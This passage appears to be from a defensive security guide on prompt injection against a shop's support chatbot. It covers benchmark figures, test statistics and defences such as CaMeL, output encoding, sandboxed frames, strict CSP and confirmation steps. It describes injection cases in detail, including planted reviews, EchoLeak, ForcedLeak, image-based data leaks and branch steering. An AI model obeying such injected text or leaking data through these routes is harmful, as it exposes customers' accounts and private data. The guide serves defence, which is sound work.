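OpenAI's own figures for GPT-5.6 look much lower. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* reports that about 0.05% of direct attacks and 3.77% of indirect ones worked on Sol, the most capable version. These rates are per attempt, so the 3.77% doesn't contradict the 20% measured after 15 tries on Gray Swan's benchmark. The two smaller versions, Terra and Luna, did slightly better than Sol in OpenAI's indirect tests, at 3.32% and 2.94%, but the other versions of GPT-5.6 did worse than Sol on Gray Swan's benchmark. A store choosing a version for its resistance to injection would therefore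 pick a different one depending on which of these two tests it used.

Anthropic has also published results with and without safeguards, the extra protections that a company puts around a model. VentureBeat, a technology news site, reported those for Opus 4.6 from its system card of February 2026. Anthropic's *Mitigating the risk of prompt injections in browser use* covers the earlier Opus 4.5:

| Model and task | Safeguards | Attempts allowed | Result |
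|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.6, programming | Off | 200 | No successes |
| Opus 4.6, controlling a computer's screen | Off | 1 | 17.8% |
| Opus 4.6, controlling a computer's screen | Off | 200 | 78.6% |
| Opus 4.6, controlling a computer's screen | On | 200 | 57.1% |
| Opus 4.5, using a browser | Off | 100 in each test environment | 8.0% of attacks |
| Opus 4.5, using a browser | Older version on | 100 in each test environment | 7.6% of attacks |
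| Opus 4.5, using a browser | Improved version on | 100 in each test environment | 1.4% of attacks |

The same model resisted every attack while programming, but most attackers succeeded when it was controlling a screen, so a company's best figure may come from a task unlike those a shop's chatbot does. Older safeguards barely helped Opus 4.5 in a browser, whereas the improved ones stopped more than four-fifths of the attacks that would otherwise have worked. Anthropic developed the improved safeguards for its own browser extension, so a shop that rents the model may not get them.

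The browser figures are the percentage of all attacks the model encountered that succeeded, not the percentage of environments where the attacker eventually succeeded. An attacker who makes 100 attempts could fail 98 or 99 times and still succeed.

Most other companies have published less that can be compared. VentureBeat compared their safety documents with Anthropic's Opus 4.8 card of May 2026. It found that Anthropic reported injection tests for four kinds of task and OpenAI for one. OpenAI's tests used known attacks on GPT-5.5's connections to other services. VentureBeat found no injection results from Google for its Gemini 3 models.

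### Small tests and repeated attempts

In Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian's tests, GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.6 resisted all ten attempts at each attack. To see how little ten trials can rule out, suppose that the attack really works with probability *p* and that the trials are independent. The chance of ten failures in a row is (1 − *p*)^10. The highest rate that would still produce such a run at least one time in 20 is the solution of:

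(1 − *p*)^10 = 0.05

This gives *p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/10) ≈ 0.26. Statisticians call this a one-sided 95% upper bound. More trials bring it down slowly:

| Independent trials without a success | Upper bound on the true success rate |
|---|---|
| 10 | 26% |
| 59 | 5% |
| 129 | 2.3% |
| 299 | 1% |
| 949 | 0.3% |

A quick estimate for larger tests is three divided by the number of trials.

The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that attacks on Opus 5 failed in all 129 browser scenarios in its system card. If each scenario counts as one independent trial, the true success rate of attacks could still be 2.3%. At that rate, an attack would have about a 75% chance of working at least once in 60 independent tries. The result is impressive, but it does not establish that 60 shoppers could safely ask about a product with a planted review.

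The bound also covers only attacks like those in the test. The failure of those attacks is weak evidence that a new one written by a more skilled attacker would fail.

Repeated attempts can succeed less often than the formula for independent trials predicts. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports that strong attacks in another Gray Swan test succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63% with 100. If each attempt had independently had a 4.7% chance of success, the rate would have been 38% with ten attempts and more than 99% with 100. The rates were most likely lower because some targets were easy to compromise and others very hard. If so, an attacker who fails repeatedly against Tarnside with one product or goal may do better by trying another.

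### Designs that limit what a review can decide

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* starts from the assumption that attackers will keep finding text that works. It proposes that once a model has read untrusted text, the software around it should make it impossible for that text to trigger a consequential action. The paper sets out six designs, each of which gives up some of the chatbot's flexibility:

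- An action selector only translates the customer's request into one of a fixed list of actions, such as showing a link to the latest order. The model never sees the results, so a review cannot influence it.
- A fixed plan commits the model to a list of tool calls before it reads any outside text. A review cannot add a call, but it may still change what goes into one.
- In a map-reduce design, a separate model without tools reads each document and returns a restricted answer, such as yes or no. Ordinary code or another model then combines the answers.
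- A dual-LLM design has a privileged model that can use tools but never reads untrusted text, and a quarantined model that reads the text but has no tools. The privileged model handles the other's results by name, without seeing their contents.
- In a code-then-execute design, the model writes a short program that calls the tools and sends untrusted text to models without tools.
- Context minimisation removes the customer's own message once the system has turned it into a database query, so that instructions in the message cannot affect the final answer.

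The paper recommends the action selector and context minimisation for its furniture shop. It assumes that the shop's chatbot does not retrieve product reviews, so it mainly addresses what customers type. Tarnside's chatbot does retrieve reviews. An action selector would protect it, but the chatbot could then not tell Maya whether the tent copes with wind.

A fixed plan leaves a less obvious gap, because untrusted text can still affect the values its steps use. Suppose Maya asks the chatbot to find the tent that reviewers like best and put it in her basket. The plan always contains the same two steps, but a planted review can change which tent the chatbot adds. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026), a survey of ways to trace what agents do, makes the general point that a text can cause harm through its influence even when its content looks innocent. To catch this, the software has to record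 where each value came from and check that record before it calls a tool.

Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues introduced a defence called CaMeL in 2025. In CaMeL, a privileged model writes a program from the user's request, and a quarantined model processes any untrusted text. An interpreter runs the program and records which sources contributed to each value. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks these records against the developer's rules. For example, a rule could forbid sending a customer's private data to an address that came from a review.

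### Maya's question under a fixed program

Maya's original question was whether order 10482 had shipped and whether the tent would cope with wind. Suppose Tarnside still has the account-closing tool, and the developers now combine the code-then-execute and map-reduce designs. The privileged model reads only Maya's question and the descriptions of the tools, and writes something like this:

```
order = lookup_order("10482")
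reviews = find_reviews("tent", topic="wind")
votes = [reader("Does it cope with wind?", r) for r in reviews]
show_answer(order.status, count(votes))
```

The server runs the program line by line. The `reader` function sends one review at a time to a model that has no tools, and the server accepts only "yes", "no" or "unclear" as an answer. Ordinary code then counts the answers and fills in a prepared reply, such as "Your order has shipped. Two of three reviews say the tent copes with wind."

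If one of the three reviews contains an injection, the attacker controls one vote. He cannot close Maya's account, because the program contains no call to that tool and nothing in a review can add one. He also cannot put markup into the answer, which can only be "yes" or "no". He can still cast a false vote, but he could have done that with an ordinary dishonest review.

Maya loses some of what made the chatbot useful. The chatbot can't quote the reviewer who camped through a storm, or mention that the tent held up only with extra pegs. The privileged model also has to plan for every result in advance, because it can't look at the order and then change its plan. For example, the program needs a branch for a cancelled order.

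Attackers can also exploit such branches. If Maya asks the chatbot to cancel her order when the reviews are bad, the program will contain a cancellation step, and a few planted reviews can trigger it. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this branch steering. CaMeL's separation of plan and data does not prevent it, because the injected text only affects which of the paths created by Maya's request the program takes. Asking Maya to confirm the cancellation would prevent the attack.

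If the developers let the reader return a full sentence and the answer to Maya includes it, that sentence becomes part of the conversation. When she asks her next question, the privileged model would read the attacker's words as an earlier message from the chatbot. The developers could avoid this by keeping such sentences out of the history that the privileged model receives.

Peters-Gill and colleagues demonstrated a similar failure between three agents that each ran CaMeL. One agent read a database of job applicants, another sent messages, and a third coordinated them. The user asked for a summary of the applicants to be sent to a colleague. The researchers had planted an instruction in the database, and the coordinator passed it along inside the summary. The messaging agent treated everything from the coordinator as a request from its user, so it also emailed the applicants' details to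 an outside address. The researchers fixed this by sending data through a separate channel that the receiving agent's privileged model cannot read. A shop that later connects its chatbot to a refunds agent would need the same separation.

### The measured cost of tracked data flow

Sources differ on how much CaMeL reduces task completion. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) says that CaMeL eliminated nearly all the attacks in AgentDojo while completing a comparable share of tasks. Peters-Gill and colleagues found a larger drop in October 2026, using five models on 112 professional tasks that required several agents to cooperate. When each agent ran CaMeL, the share of completed tasks fell by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest models, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. The separate data channel lowered the share by another 3.2 points on average,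 or 0.85 for the strongest two.

The tasks probably explain part of the difference. A program that CaMeL runs has to be written for the format of a tool's result before the tool returns one, and long tasks with several agents offer more chances to get the format wrong. The researchers had to add descriptions of every tool's output to get reasonable results. Tarnside has one or two simple tools, so its loss might be much smaller, but it would have to measure this on its own customers' questions.

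The security results came from a version of AgentDojo that the team had adapted for several agents, with 949 attacks on each model:

| Model | No CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | CaMeL with a separate data channel |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0% | 0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0% | 0% |

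The older models gained the most. GPT-5.5 had nothing to gain on this test, but Peters-Gill and colleagues warn against concluding that it is immune, because the benchmark's attacks do not adapt. The same model gave way to about one attacker in five on Gray Swan's benchmark. They also note that 949 failures are compatible with a true rate of up to 0.4%. (Their figure is slightly higher than the 0.3% above because they used a two-sided interval.)

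Zero successful attacks is a more convincing result for CaMeL than for a trained model because, if the interpreter works correctly, text in a tool's result cannot add a step to the program, however the attacker phrases it. The guarantee doesn't cover false votes, branch steering or bugs in the interpreter. The researchers tested CaMeL without any rules about where data may go, so the results show how well it protects the plan, but not how well a developer's rules would protect a customer's address.

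Shumailov, Carlini and Florian Tramèr contributed to the evidence on both sides of this comparison. They helped to develop CaMeL and took part in the tests that defeated the 12 other defences, and Tramèr is also a co-author of the design patterns. Their attacks are convincing because a successful attack shows that a defence can be broken, whoever carries it out. The claims for their own design would benefit more from independent tests.

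### Whether better models will be enough

The NCSC doubts that anyone will ever fully prevent prompt injection. Its doubt is based on how LLMs process text, which more training doesn't change. OpenAI, which has an interest in saying otherwise, conceded in December 2025 that the problem may never be fully solved, according to The Decoder.

Anthropic is more hopeful. When it released Opus 4.5, it called prompt injection "far from a solved problem" but said it was aiming for agents that can handle valuable tasks without significant risk. The evidence since then partly supports its optimism. On Gray Swan's benchmark, the attack success rate within 15 attempts fell by more than half between Opus 4.8 and Opus 5. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Opus 5 says that resistance to injection improved more than anything else in its tests of agents' safety. Anthropic ran most of the card's tests itself,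 though Gray Swan's benchmark is external.

These positions are compatible, because the NCSC doubts that the rate will ever reach zero and Anthropic hopes to make it low enough to accept. The acceptable rate depends on what the attacker can gain. Tarnside can apologise if an injected review makes its chatbot praise the wrong tent once in 500 conversations. But if the chatbot closes an account that often, a busy shop could lose one every day, and removing the tool that closes accounts or setting the program in advance would be far safer than waiting for the next model.

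Better models are still the more useful remedy for some harms. No fixed program can tell whether a review that says the tent leaks is honest, so an owner who wants the chatbot to quote reviewers freely has to rely on the model's judgement about what to repeat. But the recent gains are limited to particular models, so a small shop whose plugin still uses GPT-4.1 won't benefit from Opus 5's improvements until somebody changes the model.

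## Defences that hold when the model obeys the attacker

These defences assume that the attacker controls everything Tarnside's model writes, including its tool calls. OWASP advises developers to treat the model like any other user, so the widget should handle the model's answer as carefully as a review posted by a stranger, and the server should check a tool call as strictly as a request from an unknown browser. These checks are ordinary code, so they work even if the model fails to detect the attack.

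### Encoding text for its place in the page

Encoding makes the browser display the model's markup as plain text. Here is a harmless answer before and after:

| | The model's answer |
|---|---|
| Before encoding | `<b>tent</b> & "pegs"` |
| After encoding | `&lt;b&gt;tent&lt;/b&gt; &amp; &quot;pegs&quot;` |

OWASP's *Cross Site Scripting Prevention Cheat Sheet* lists five characters to encode between HTML tags: the ampersand, the two angle brackets, and the single and double quotation marks. Other parts of a page follow different rules, so the developer has to match the encoding to the place. Here is the phrase `tent & pegs` in several places:

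| Where the model's text goes | What the store's code should do | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Between two tags | Encode it for HTML | `tent &amp; pegs` |
| In a picture's description | Encode it and put quotation marks around it | `alt="tent &amp; pegs"` |
| In a link, as a search term | Encode the term for a web address, then encode the whole address for HTML | `?q=tent%20%26%20pegs` |
| As the whole address of a link | Check the address, since encoding is not enough | Only approved addresses |
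| As code inside a script | Never put it there | None |

Encoding cannot make a whole address safe because an address that runs code may contain none of the five characters. The widget has to parse the address and accept only ordinary web links.

The safest way to display plain text is to assign it to an element's `textContent` property, which never parses HTML. The developer should pass the original string, because if the widget encoded it first, Maya would see codes such as `&lt;` instead of the characters they represent. Popular web frameworks also encode text by default, but they include ways to skip this step. React's is a property called `dangerouslySetInnerHTML`, so searching for that name is a quick way to find risky code in a React widget.

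Tarnside should save the model's original answer and encode it each time it is displayed. OWASP warns against a general filter that encodes text as it enters the application, because the filter has no information about where the text will appear. An answer encoded for a web page would show stray codes in a plain-text email and would still be unsafe inside a script.

### Sanitising formatted answers

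Encoding the whole answer would also disable the bold text, lists and links that Tarnside wants. If the store keeps them, the widget should process each answer in this order:

1. The Markdown parser converts everything received so far into HTML.
2. The sanitiser removes every tag and attribute that is not on a short list.
3. The widget checks the address of each remaining link.
4. The widget inserts the result, and no other code changes it afterwards.

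A support chatbot needs few HTML tags. Tarnside could allow paragraphs, bold and italic text, lists, and links to its own site. This would exclude images, forms, frames and the `style` attribute, which an attacker could use to cover the page with a false notice. A list of allowed tags is safer than a list of forbidden ones because any tag the developer forgot is removed instead of getting through.

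The EchoLeak attack on Microsoft's Copilot shows why the checks belong after the conversion from Markdown to HTML. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reports that Copilot's filter removed links in the usual Markdown form but missed reference-style links, which put the address on a separate line. Both forms become the same HTML element, so a check after conversion would not have had to recognise each way of writing a link.

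Sanitisers also have bugs. OWASP recommends the DOMPurify library but tells developers to update it regularly, because researchers keep finding ways around such libraries. A June 2026 advisory reproduced in CIRCL's *CWE-79* reports that DOMPurify could leave executable markup in place when it cleaned existing page elements from another frame. A widget that passes the library a string and inserts the returned string does not use that mode.

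A browser feature called Trusted Types helps with code that the developers overlooked. When a site turns it on, the browser stops `innerHTML` and similar functions from accepting an ordinary string. The string must first pass through a function that the developers have approved, which can call the sanitiser. This would probably have exposed AnythingLLM's unprotected chart captions, because they would have stopped displaying. OWASP describes the feature for Chromium-based browsers such as Chrome, and counts it among the few controls that remove whole classes of DOM-based XSS. It gives no protection if the approved function returns every string unchanged.

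### Product cards that the store builds

To build product cards itself, Tarnside can require the model to answer in a fixed format:

```
{"text": "This tent copes well with wind.", "product_id": "T-204"}
```

The server looks up T-204 in the catalogue and builds a card from the name, price, picture and link stored there. If the catalogue has no such number, the server leaves the card out. An attacker who controls the model can make it recommend the wrong tent but cannot change the price or link the button to another site.

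The `text` field still needs encoding, because valid JSON can contain any markup. The server should also reject fields it does not expect. Otherwise a model could add an `image_url` field, and the image leak would return if a developer later made the widget display it.

### A frame on a separate domain

Tarnside can also prepare for a mistake in the widget by moving the chat into a frame:

`<iframe src="https://tarnside-chat.example" sandbox="allow-scripts"></iframe>`

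The `sandbox` attribute removes most of a framed page's abilities, and each keyword in its value restores one. Here the page may run scripts, but the browser gives it an origin that matches no other page. If an attacker's script runs in the chat, the same-origin rule stops it from reading Maya's account page or operating the forms on it.

A script in the frame can reach the surrounding page and remove the sandbox if the framed page comes from the store's own origin and the developers add `allow-same-origin`. A subdomain such as `chat.tarnside.example` also gives less protection than a separate domain. It is a different origin from the main shop, but browsers treat the two as the same site when they decide whether to attach certain cookies. A script there might be able to send requests with Maya's cookie, although it could not read the replies.

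The chat still has to identify Maya, so the store's page can give the frame a short-lived token that only allows it to send chat messages. A script that stole the token could ask the chatbot about Maya's orders until the token expired, but could not use it to change her email address. The frame and the page may also need to exchange messages, for instance to resize the chat window. The page should accept only the exact messages it expects from that frame and never insert their contents as HTML.

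The widget still needs encoding and sanitising, because a script in the frame can read the conversation and imitate a login form.

### What a strict Content Security Policy blocks

Weichselbaum, in *Mitigate cross-site scripting (XSS) with a strict Content Security Policy (CSP)*, gives this basic policy:

```
Content-Security-Policy:
  script-src 'nonce-{RANDOM}' 'strict-dynamic';
  object-src 'none';
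  base-uri 'none';
```

The nonce is a random value that the server generates for each response and puts in the header and in its own script tags. The browser does not run a script tag without it. With `'strict-dynamic'`, an approved script may load further scripts, which most third-party widgets need to do. The last two lines disable old plugins and stop an injected tag from changing where the page's relative addresses lead.

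If the server sends the same stored page to everyone, it cannot insert a fresh nonce. The policy can instead identify each approved inline script by its hash, a short value computed from the script's exact text. Many sites still use an older kind of policy that lists the hosts scripts may load from. Weichselbaum says attackers can bypass most of these policies.

The basic policy has no rules for images or forms, so Tarnside should add `img-src` and `form-action`. The table assumes that these permit only the store's own addresses:

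| What reaches the page in the model's answer | Basic policy | With image and form rules |
|---|---|---|
| A script tag or an attribute that holds code | Blocks it | Blocks it |
| A link whose address would run code | Blocks it | Blocks it |
| Markup from which an approved script builds a new script element | May let it run | May let it run |
| An image on the attacker's server | Loads it | Blocks it |
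| A form that sends data to the attacker | Allows it | Blocks it |
| An ordinary link that Maya has to click | Allows it | Allows it |
| A false sentence | Displays it | Displays it |

The third row describes a particular risk for chat widgets. jQuery, an old but common web library, has an `.html()` function that can create script elements from the text it receives. Weichselbaum lists this function among the cases where a strict policy may not help. If an approved widget uses it to display answers, `'strict-dynamic'` may allow the attacker's script too.

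Reddy and Gujral would go further and forbid all scripts wherever the model's output appears. A shop's page needs scripts to work, but the store could apply this rule to a small frame that only displays finished answers. OWASP recommends CSP only as an additional layer because developers easily make mistakes with it.

### Image leaks through permitted hosts

An `img-src` rule controls which host the browser contacts, but not what that host does with the request. Superhuman's policy allowed a Google domain where attackers could create forms, and Copilot's allowed a Microsoft service that forwarded requests. In April 2026, PromptArmor's *codex for everything exfiltrates connected data* reported that OpenAI's Codex could also be made to send a user's emails to a Google Form through an image. It says OpenAI has fixed this.

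A safe host can also become unsafe. Willison's *ForcedLeak* describes an attack on Salesforce's AI agents that began with text in a form for sales enquiries. Salesforce's policy still permitted images from a domain whose registration had expired. The researchers registered the domain themselves and received details of sales contacts in their server's log. Salesforce corrected the policy and added a separate check on the addresses its agents may use. It also recovered the domain, according to Salesforce Ben, a news site about the company's products.

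GitHub had a stronger control. When a page includes an outside image, GitHub replaces the image's address with a signed one that leads to GitHub's own proxy, which fetches the image only if the signature is valid. SecurityWeek explains that an attacker therefore could not leak private text by having GitHub's AI assistant write it into a new address. The researcher instead prepared a dictionary of validly signed addresses, so that the assistant could convey the text through its choice of images. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* reports that GitHub fixed the leak by turning off images in the assistant's chat completely.

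This case is a reason to doubt one of Reddy and Gujral's ratings. They expect a signed proxy to block leaks like this, but they ran no experiments, and GitHub's signatures did not prevent this one. A signature shows only that GitHub approved an address, not that the sequence of requests is harmless.

Tarnside has little need for images in the model's text if its product cards already contain pictures. If it keeps those images in the text, it should allow only catalogue pictures from a server that does not forward requests and whose logs outsiders cannot read. PromptArmor gave similar advice to Notion, a note-taking service, after finding a data leak through images there.

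### Whether CSP trusts AI-generated content

McHugh and colleagues claim that CSP filters "whitelist AI-generated content as trusted", but they give no test or source, and browsers do not apply a policy that way. A browser checks where a script came from, whether it carries the right nonce, or whether its text matches an approved hash, and the policy has no way to specify who or what wrote the script.

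The server never gives the model the nonce, so any script tag the model writes lacks it, and the browser refuses to run the script. A strict policy also blocks the DeepSeek attack that McHugh and colleagues print as their example, which used a frame with code in its address.

Developers can accidentally make a content security policy allow scripts in a chatbot's answer. OWASP's *Content Security Policy Cheat Sheet* warns against code that automatically adds the nonce to every script tag in a finished page, because it will also approve an attacker's tags. Tarnside would have this problem if its server built a transcript page from saved answers and then added nonces to every script tag in it. A policy with `'unsafe-inline'` and no nonce or hash would also allow inline scripts, whether they were in a chatbot's answer or a human's comment.

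The cases in which researchers demonstrated scripts suggest that many failures have a simpler cause, the lack of an adequate policy. Neither the bank that Positive Security tested nor Quarkslab's client had one.

### Cookie flags

A site sets flags on its session cookie to tell the browser how to handle it:

| Flag | What the browser does | What the flag does not stop |
|---|---|---|
| HttpOnly | Hides the cookie from scripts | A script that sends requests from Maya's open page |
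| Secure | Sends the cookie only over encrypted connections | A script on an encrypted page |
| SameSite=Lax | Withholds the cookie from most requests that other sites start, but sends it when Maya follows a link | A script on the store's own site |
| SameSite=Strict | Also withholds the cookie when Maya follows a link from another site | A script on the store's own site |

HttpOnly stops a script from copying the session cookie, but the script can still act within the session because the browser attaches the cookie to its requests. Without a copy, the attacker has to act while the page is open, unless he makes a lasting change, such as replacing the email address on the account.

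The SameSite setting Strict can annoy customers, since Maya would appear logged out when she followed a link in an order email. Lax avoids this, but it doesn't protect the store if following a link is enough to change anything. The server should accept changes only through requests that carry an anti-CSRF token.

The chatbot's own functions need the same token. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a scenario in which a malicious page makes a logged-in user's browser save a false payment address in an AI assistant's memory. The assistant repeats the address days later, when the user asks how to pay. They constructed this example and did not test it. The forged request that saves the address is ordinary CSRF, which a token would prevent. The rest of the attack is specific to AI assistants, because it relies on the model treating its memory as accurate. If a store left the function that receives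 chat messages unprotected, another site could also submit instructions to the chatbot in Maya's name.

### Fresh proof for sensitive actions

A session shows only that Maya logged in at some point, so Tarnside should ask for her password or a code from her phone before it changes an email address or password, closes an account or issues a large refund. A "Confirm" button is not enough, because a script can press it on a page it controls. The script would not have the password or code unless Maya entered it on that page.

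The application, rather than the model, should ask the customer to confirm tool calls. When the model calls the tool to close an account, the server saves the request without carrying it out. The widget then shows a fixed notice, such as "Close your Tarnside account permanently?", and sends the customer's password directly to the server. The server performs only the saved request, so the model cannot show one action and run another. Typing "yes" in the chat should have no effect, because the model could misreport or invent that reply.

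A customer may still approve something after reading convincing but false information from the chatbot, so the notice should state the consequences plainly. When somebody changes the email address on an account, Tarnside can also email the old address and wait a day before allowing password resets through the new one. These steps do not stop the change, but they give Maya a chance to reverse it.

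### Ownership checks and the shopper's rights

The order tool should take the customer's identity from the session and have no input field for it, so that even a model that fully obeys the attacker cannot specify another customer.

The same rule applies to conversations. If someone requests another customer's conversation, the server should respond as though that conversation did not exist. Long random identifiers are harder to guess, but the server must still check who owns the conversation, because someone may get the identifier from a shared link or a log.

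Customers who order without an account have no session to check, and an order number is weak proof, as Yuma AI's chatbot showed. Tarnside can send a single-use link to the email address already on the order, never to one that the model or the visitor supplies. The chatbot can confirm that it has sent the link without revealing the address.

A tool that runs with Maya's rights can still harm her, because she has the right to close her own account. Tarnside should therefore remove tools the chatbot does not need and limit what the others return. If `lookup_order` returns only the delivery status, an injected review cannot make the model leak her address from that lookup.

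### Database roles for queries that the model writes

If the model writes database queries, they should run under a read-only account. This would have stopped the deletions and the change of email address in Pedro and colleagues' tests, but not the query that read the whole table of users.

The developers can close that gap with a view, which exposes only selected columns and rows of a table, or with a database rule that adds Maya's customer number to every query. The server has to set that number from her session, and the model's query must not be able to change it. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian also recommend parsing each query before it runs, so that the application can reject queries that use forbidden tables or operations.

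Ready-made security products may not supply these limits. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian looked at Guardrails AI, a framework that checks a model's inputs and outputs, and found that most of its checks did not directly apply to their attacks, though one on SQL queries did. They reviewed only this framework, so others may offer more.

### Limits on outbound requests

TicketOracle's fetching tool was dangerous because the model could give it any address. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend that the model supply only a concert's identifier and that the application build the address from it. Tarnside could do the same with product numbers.

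If a tool must fetch outside pages, its code should check the address the server will contact. Comparing the address with a list of forbidden names is not enough, because one address can be written in several ways and a permitted page can redirect to an internal one. In an attack called DNS rebinding, a domain name leads to a public server during the check and to an internal one a moment later. The tool can prevent this by looking up the name once and connecting only to the address it has checked. It should repeat the check for every redirect.

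Tarnside can use a firewall, which works outside the tool's code, to block all outbound requests from the chatbot's server except those to a few services it needs, such as the model's provider. This prevents requests to internal systems and to an attacker's own server, but data can still leak through a permitted host if outsiders can collect it there. Internal services should also require a login, so that a request does not gain access just because it comes from the right computer.

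### The support agent's console

A script that fails in Maya's widget may succeed in the console where an agent reads the same conversation. Tarnside should use the same code to display answers in both places, because if two teams maintain separate versions, one may add a format that the other has never sanitised.

The console should have stricter settings because the agent has more access. It can show conversations as plain text and leave out images, since an attacker could use an image to detect when an agent opens the chat. It should open attachments on a separate domain, where a script in a file cannot use the agent's session. The agent, too, should have to prove their identity again before issuing a refund or changing a customer's email address.

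These rules also apply to places developers forget, such as emailed transcripts, exported reports and the page where administrators read the logs. That page is a valuable target for the kind of blind XSS that Positive Security considered.

### Logs that lead back to a review

OWASP recommends monitoring the model's outputs for unusual patterns, and Reddy and Gujral would also record prompts, sources and outgoing requests. To trace a planted review, Tarnside needs to know exactly what the model read. A record for one answer could contain:

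| Field | Example |
|---|---|
| Conversation and customer | 7731, customer 5512 |
| Model and system prompt versions | Model 4, prompt 12 |
| Retrieved text and its role | Review 904, second edit, full text, tool role |
| Tool call and arguments | `lookup_order`, order 10482 |
| Server's decision | Allowed, order belongs to customer 5512 |
| Model's original answer | Saved before encoding or sanitising |

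Suppose Maya complains that the chatbot added "marmalade" to its answer. The developers open the log and find that word in review 904. They then search for every other conversation that retrieved the review, to see who else may have received the injected answer and whether any tool calls followed. The log has to contain the text as the model read it, because the attacker may have edited the review since.

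The developers then remove the review from the product page, the chatbot's searchable copy and any saved summaries. If the answers contained a script, the developers should end the affected customers' sessions and check for recent changes to email addresses. They should keep the evidence in a form that no browser will run.

A strict CSP can provide an earlier warning, because browsers can report content that the policy blocks. A sudden series of blocked scripts on pages with the chat widget would justify searching the logs, though some reports will have harmless causes, such as browser extensions.

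Logs also contain customers' questions and addresses. Tarnside should restrict who can read the logs, delete them after a fixed period, and never record passwords or session cookies in them.

### Which defence acts on which link

In this table, "breaks" assumes the developers have applied the measure everywhere it is needed. "Reduces" means some attacks still get through, and "limits" means the measure leaves the attacker less to gain.

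| Defence | Link in the attack | Effect | What remains possible |
|---|---|---|---|
| History stored or signed by the server | A visitor forges earlier messages | Breaks | Instructions in new messages or reviews |
| Reviews kept out of the chatbot | A planted review reaches the model | Breaks | Text from other outside sources |
| Model training, marked text and filters | The model obeys | Reduces | Success after repeated attempts |
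| Encoding | The answer becomes markup | Breaks | False statements and tool calls |
| Sanitising after conversion | The answer becomes a script | Breaks, while the sanitiser has no known bypass | Misleading text and permitted links |
| Product cards built by the store | The model supplies a card's markup or address | Breaks | Recommending the wrong product |
| Chat frame on a separate domain | A script reaches the account page | Breaks | Reading the chat, showing a false login form |
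| Strict CSP | A script runs | Reduces | Scripts created by approved code |
| Images only from the store's catalogue | An image carries data to the attacker | Breaks, if outsiders cannot see or receive the requests | Links that the customer clicks |
| HttpOnly | A script copies the session cookie | Breaks | Actions within the session |
| Anti-CSRF tokens, with SameSite cookies | Another site sends a request in Maya's name | Breaks | Requests from a script on the store's page |
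| Password or code for sensitive actions | A script or tool changes the account silently | Breaks | Deceiving the customer into approving |
| Ownership checks | A visitor obtains someone else's order or chat | Breaks | Access through the owner's session |
| Tools with only the shopper's rights | The model reaches other customers' data | Breaks | Harm to the shopper's own account |
| Tools that return fewer fields | The model leaks a customer's record | Limits | Leaking the remaining fields |
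| Read-only database role | A query changes or deletes data | Breaks | Reading everything the role can see |
| Outbound allow-list | The server contacts a forbidden host | Breaks | Misuse of permitted hosts |
| Detailed logs | A planted review keeps working unnoticed | Limits | Harm before anyone investigates |

### An order of work for a small store

A small store often adds its chatbot by pasting a vendor's script into its pages. That script runs with the same access as the store's own code, and the owner usually cannot change how it displays answers. The defences below start with settings that take minutes to change and leave the technical work until later.

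1. **Switch off what the chatbot does not need.** The owner should start with tools that change accounts or issue refunds, then consider customer reviews, memory and images.
2. **Update the widget and test how it displays answers.** The owner can ask for `<b>tent</b>` and check the chat window, the agent's console and any emailed transcript. If the word is bold, the owner should turn off HTML or take the widget off every page that shares an origin with customers' accounts until the vendor fixes it. Visible tags are less conclusive, so the vendor should also confirm that its code encodes or sanitises every answer.
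3. **Test the store with two customer accounts.** One account should not be able to open the other's orders or conversations, either through the chatbot or by changing a number in an address.
4. **Protect the account pages.** Changes of email address and password should require the current password or a code, and the session cookie should have all three flags. On a hosted shop, the platform may control these settings, so the owner may have to ask its support team.
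5. **Move the chat to a separate domain.** Some vendors offer a framed version or a standalone chat page. If this one does not, a developer can put its script on an otherwise empty page on another domain and frame that page.
6. **Add a CSP in report-only mode.** The browser then reports what the policy would have blocked without breaking the shop, and the owner can enforce it once the reports look harmless. A hash is awkward for a vendor's script because, as 18F's *Content Security Policy* notes, the store has to compute a new one after every change. A nonce with `'strict-dynamic'` avoids this, at the price of trusting whatever the vendor's script loads.
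7. **Ask the vendor for its records.** The owner needs to see which passages the chatbot retrieved and which tools it called, and needs a way to delete a passage from the chatbot's copy of the site. If the vendor cannot provide this, the chatbot should not read customer reviews.
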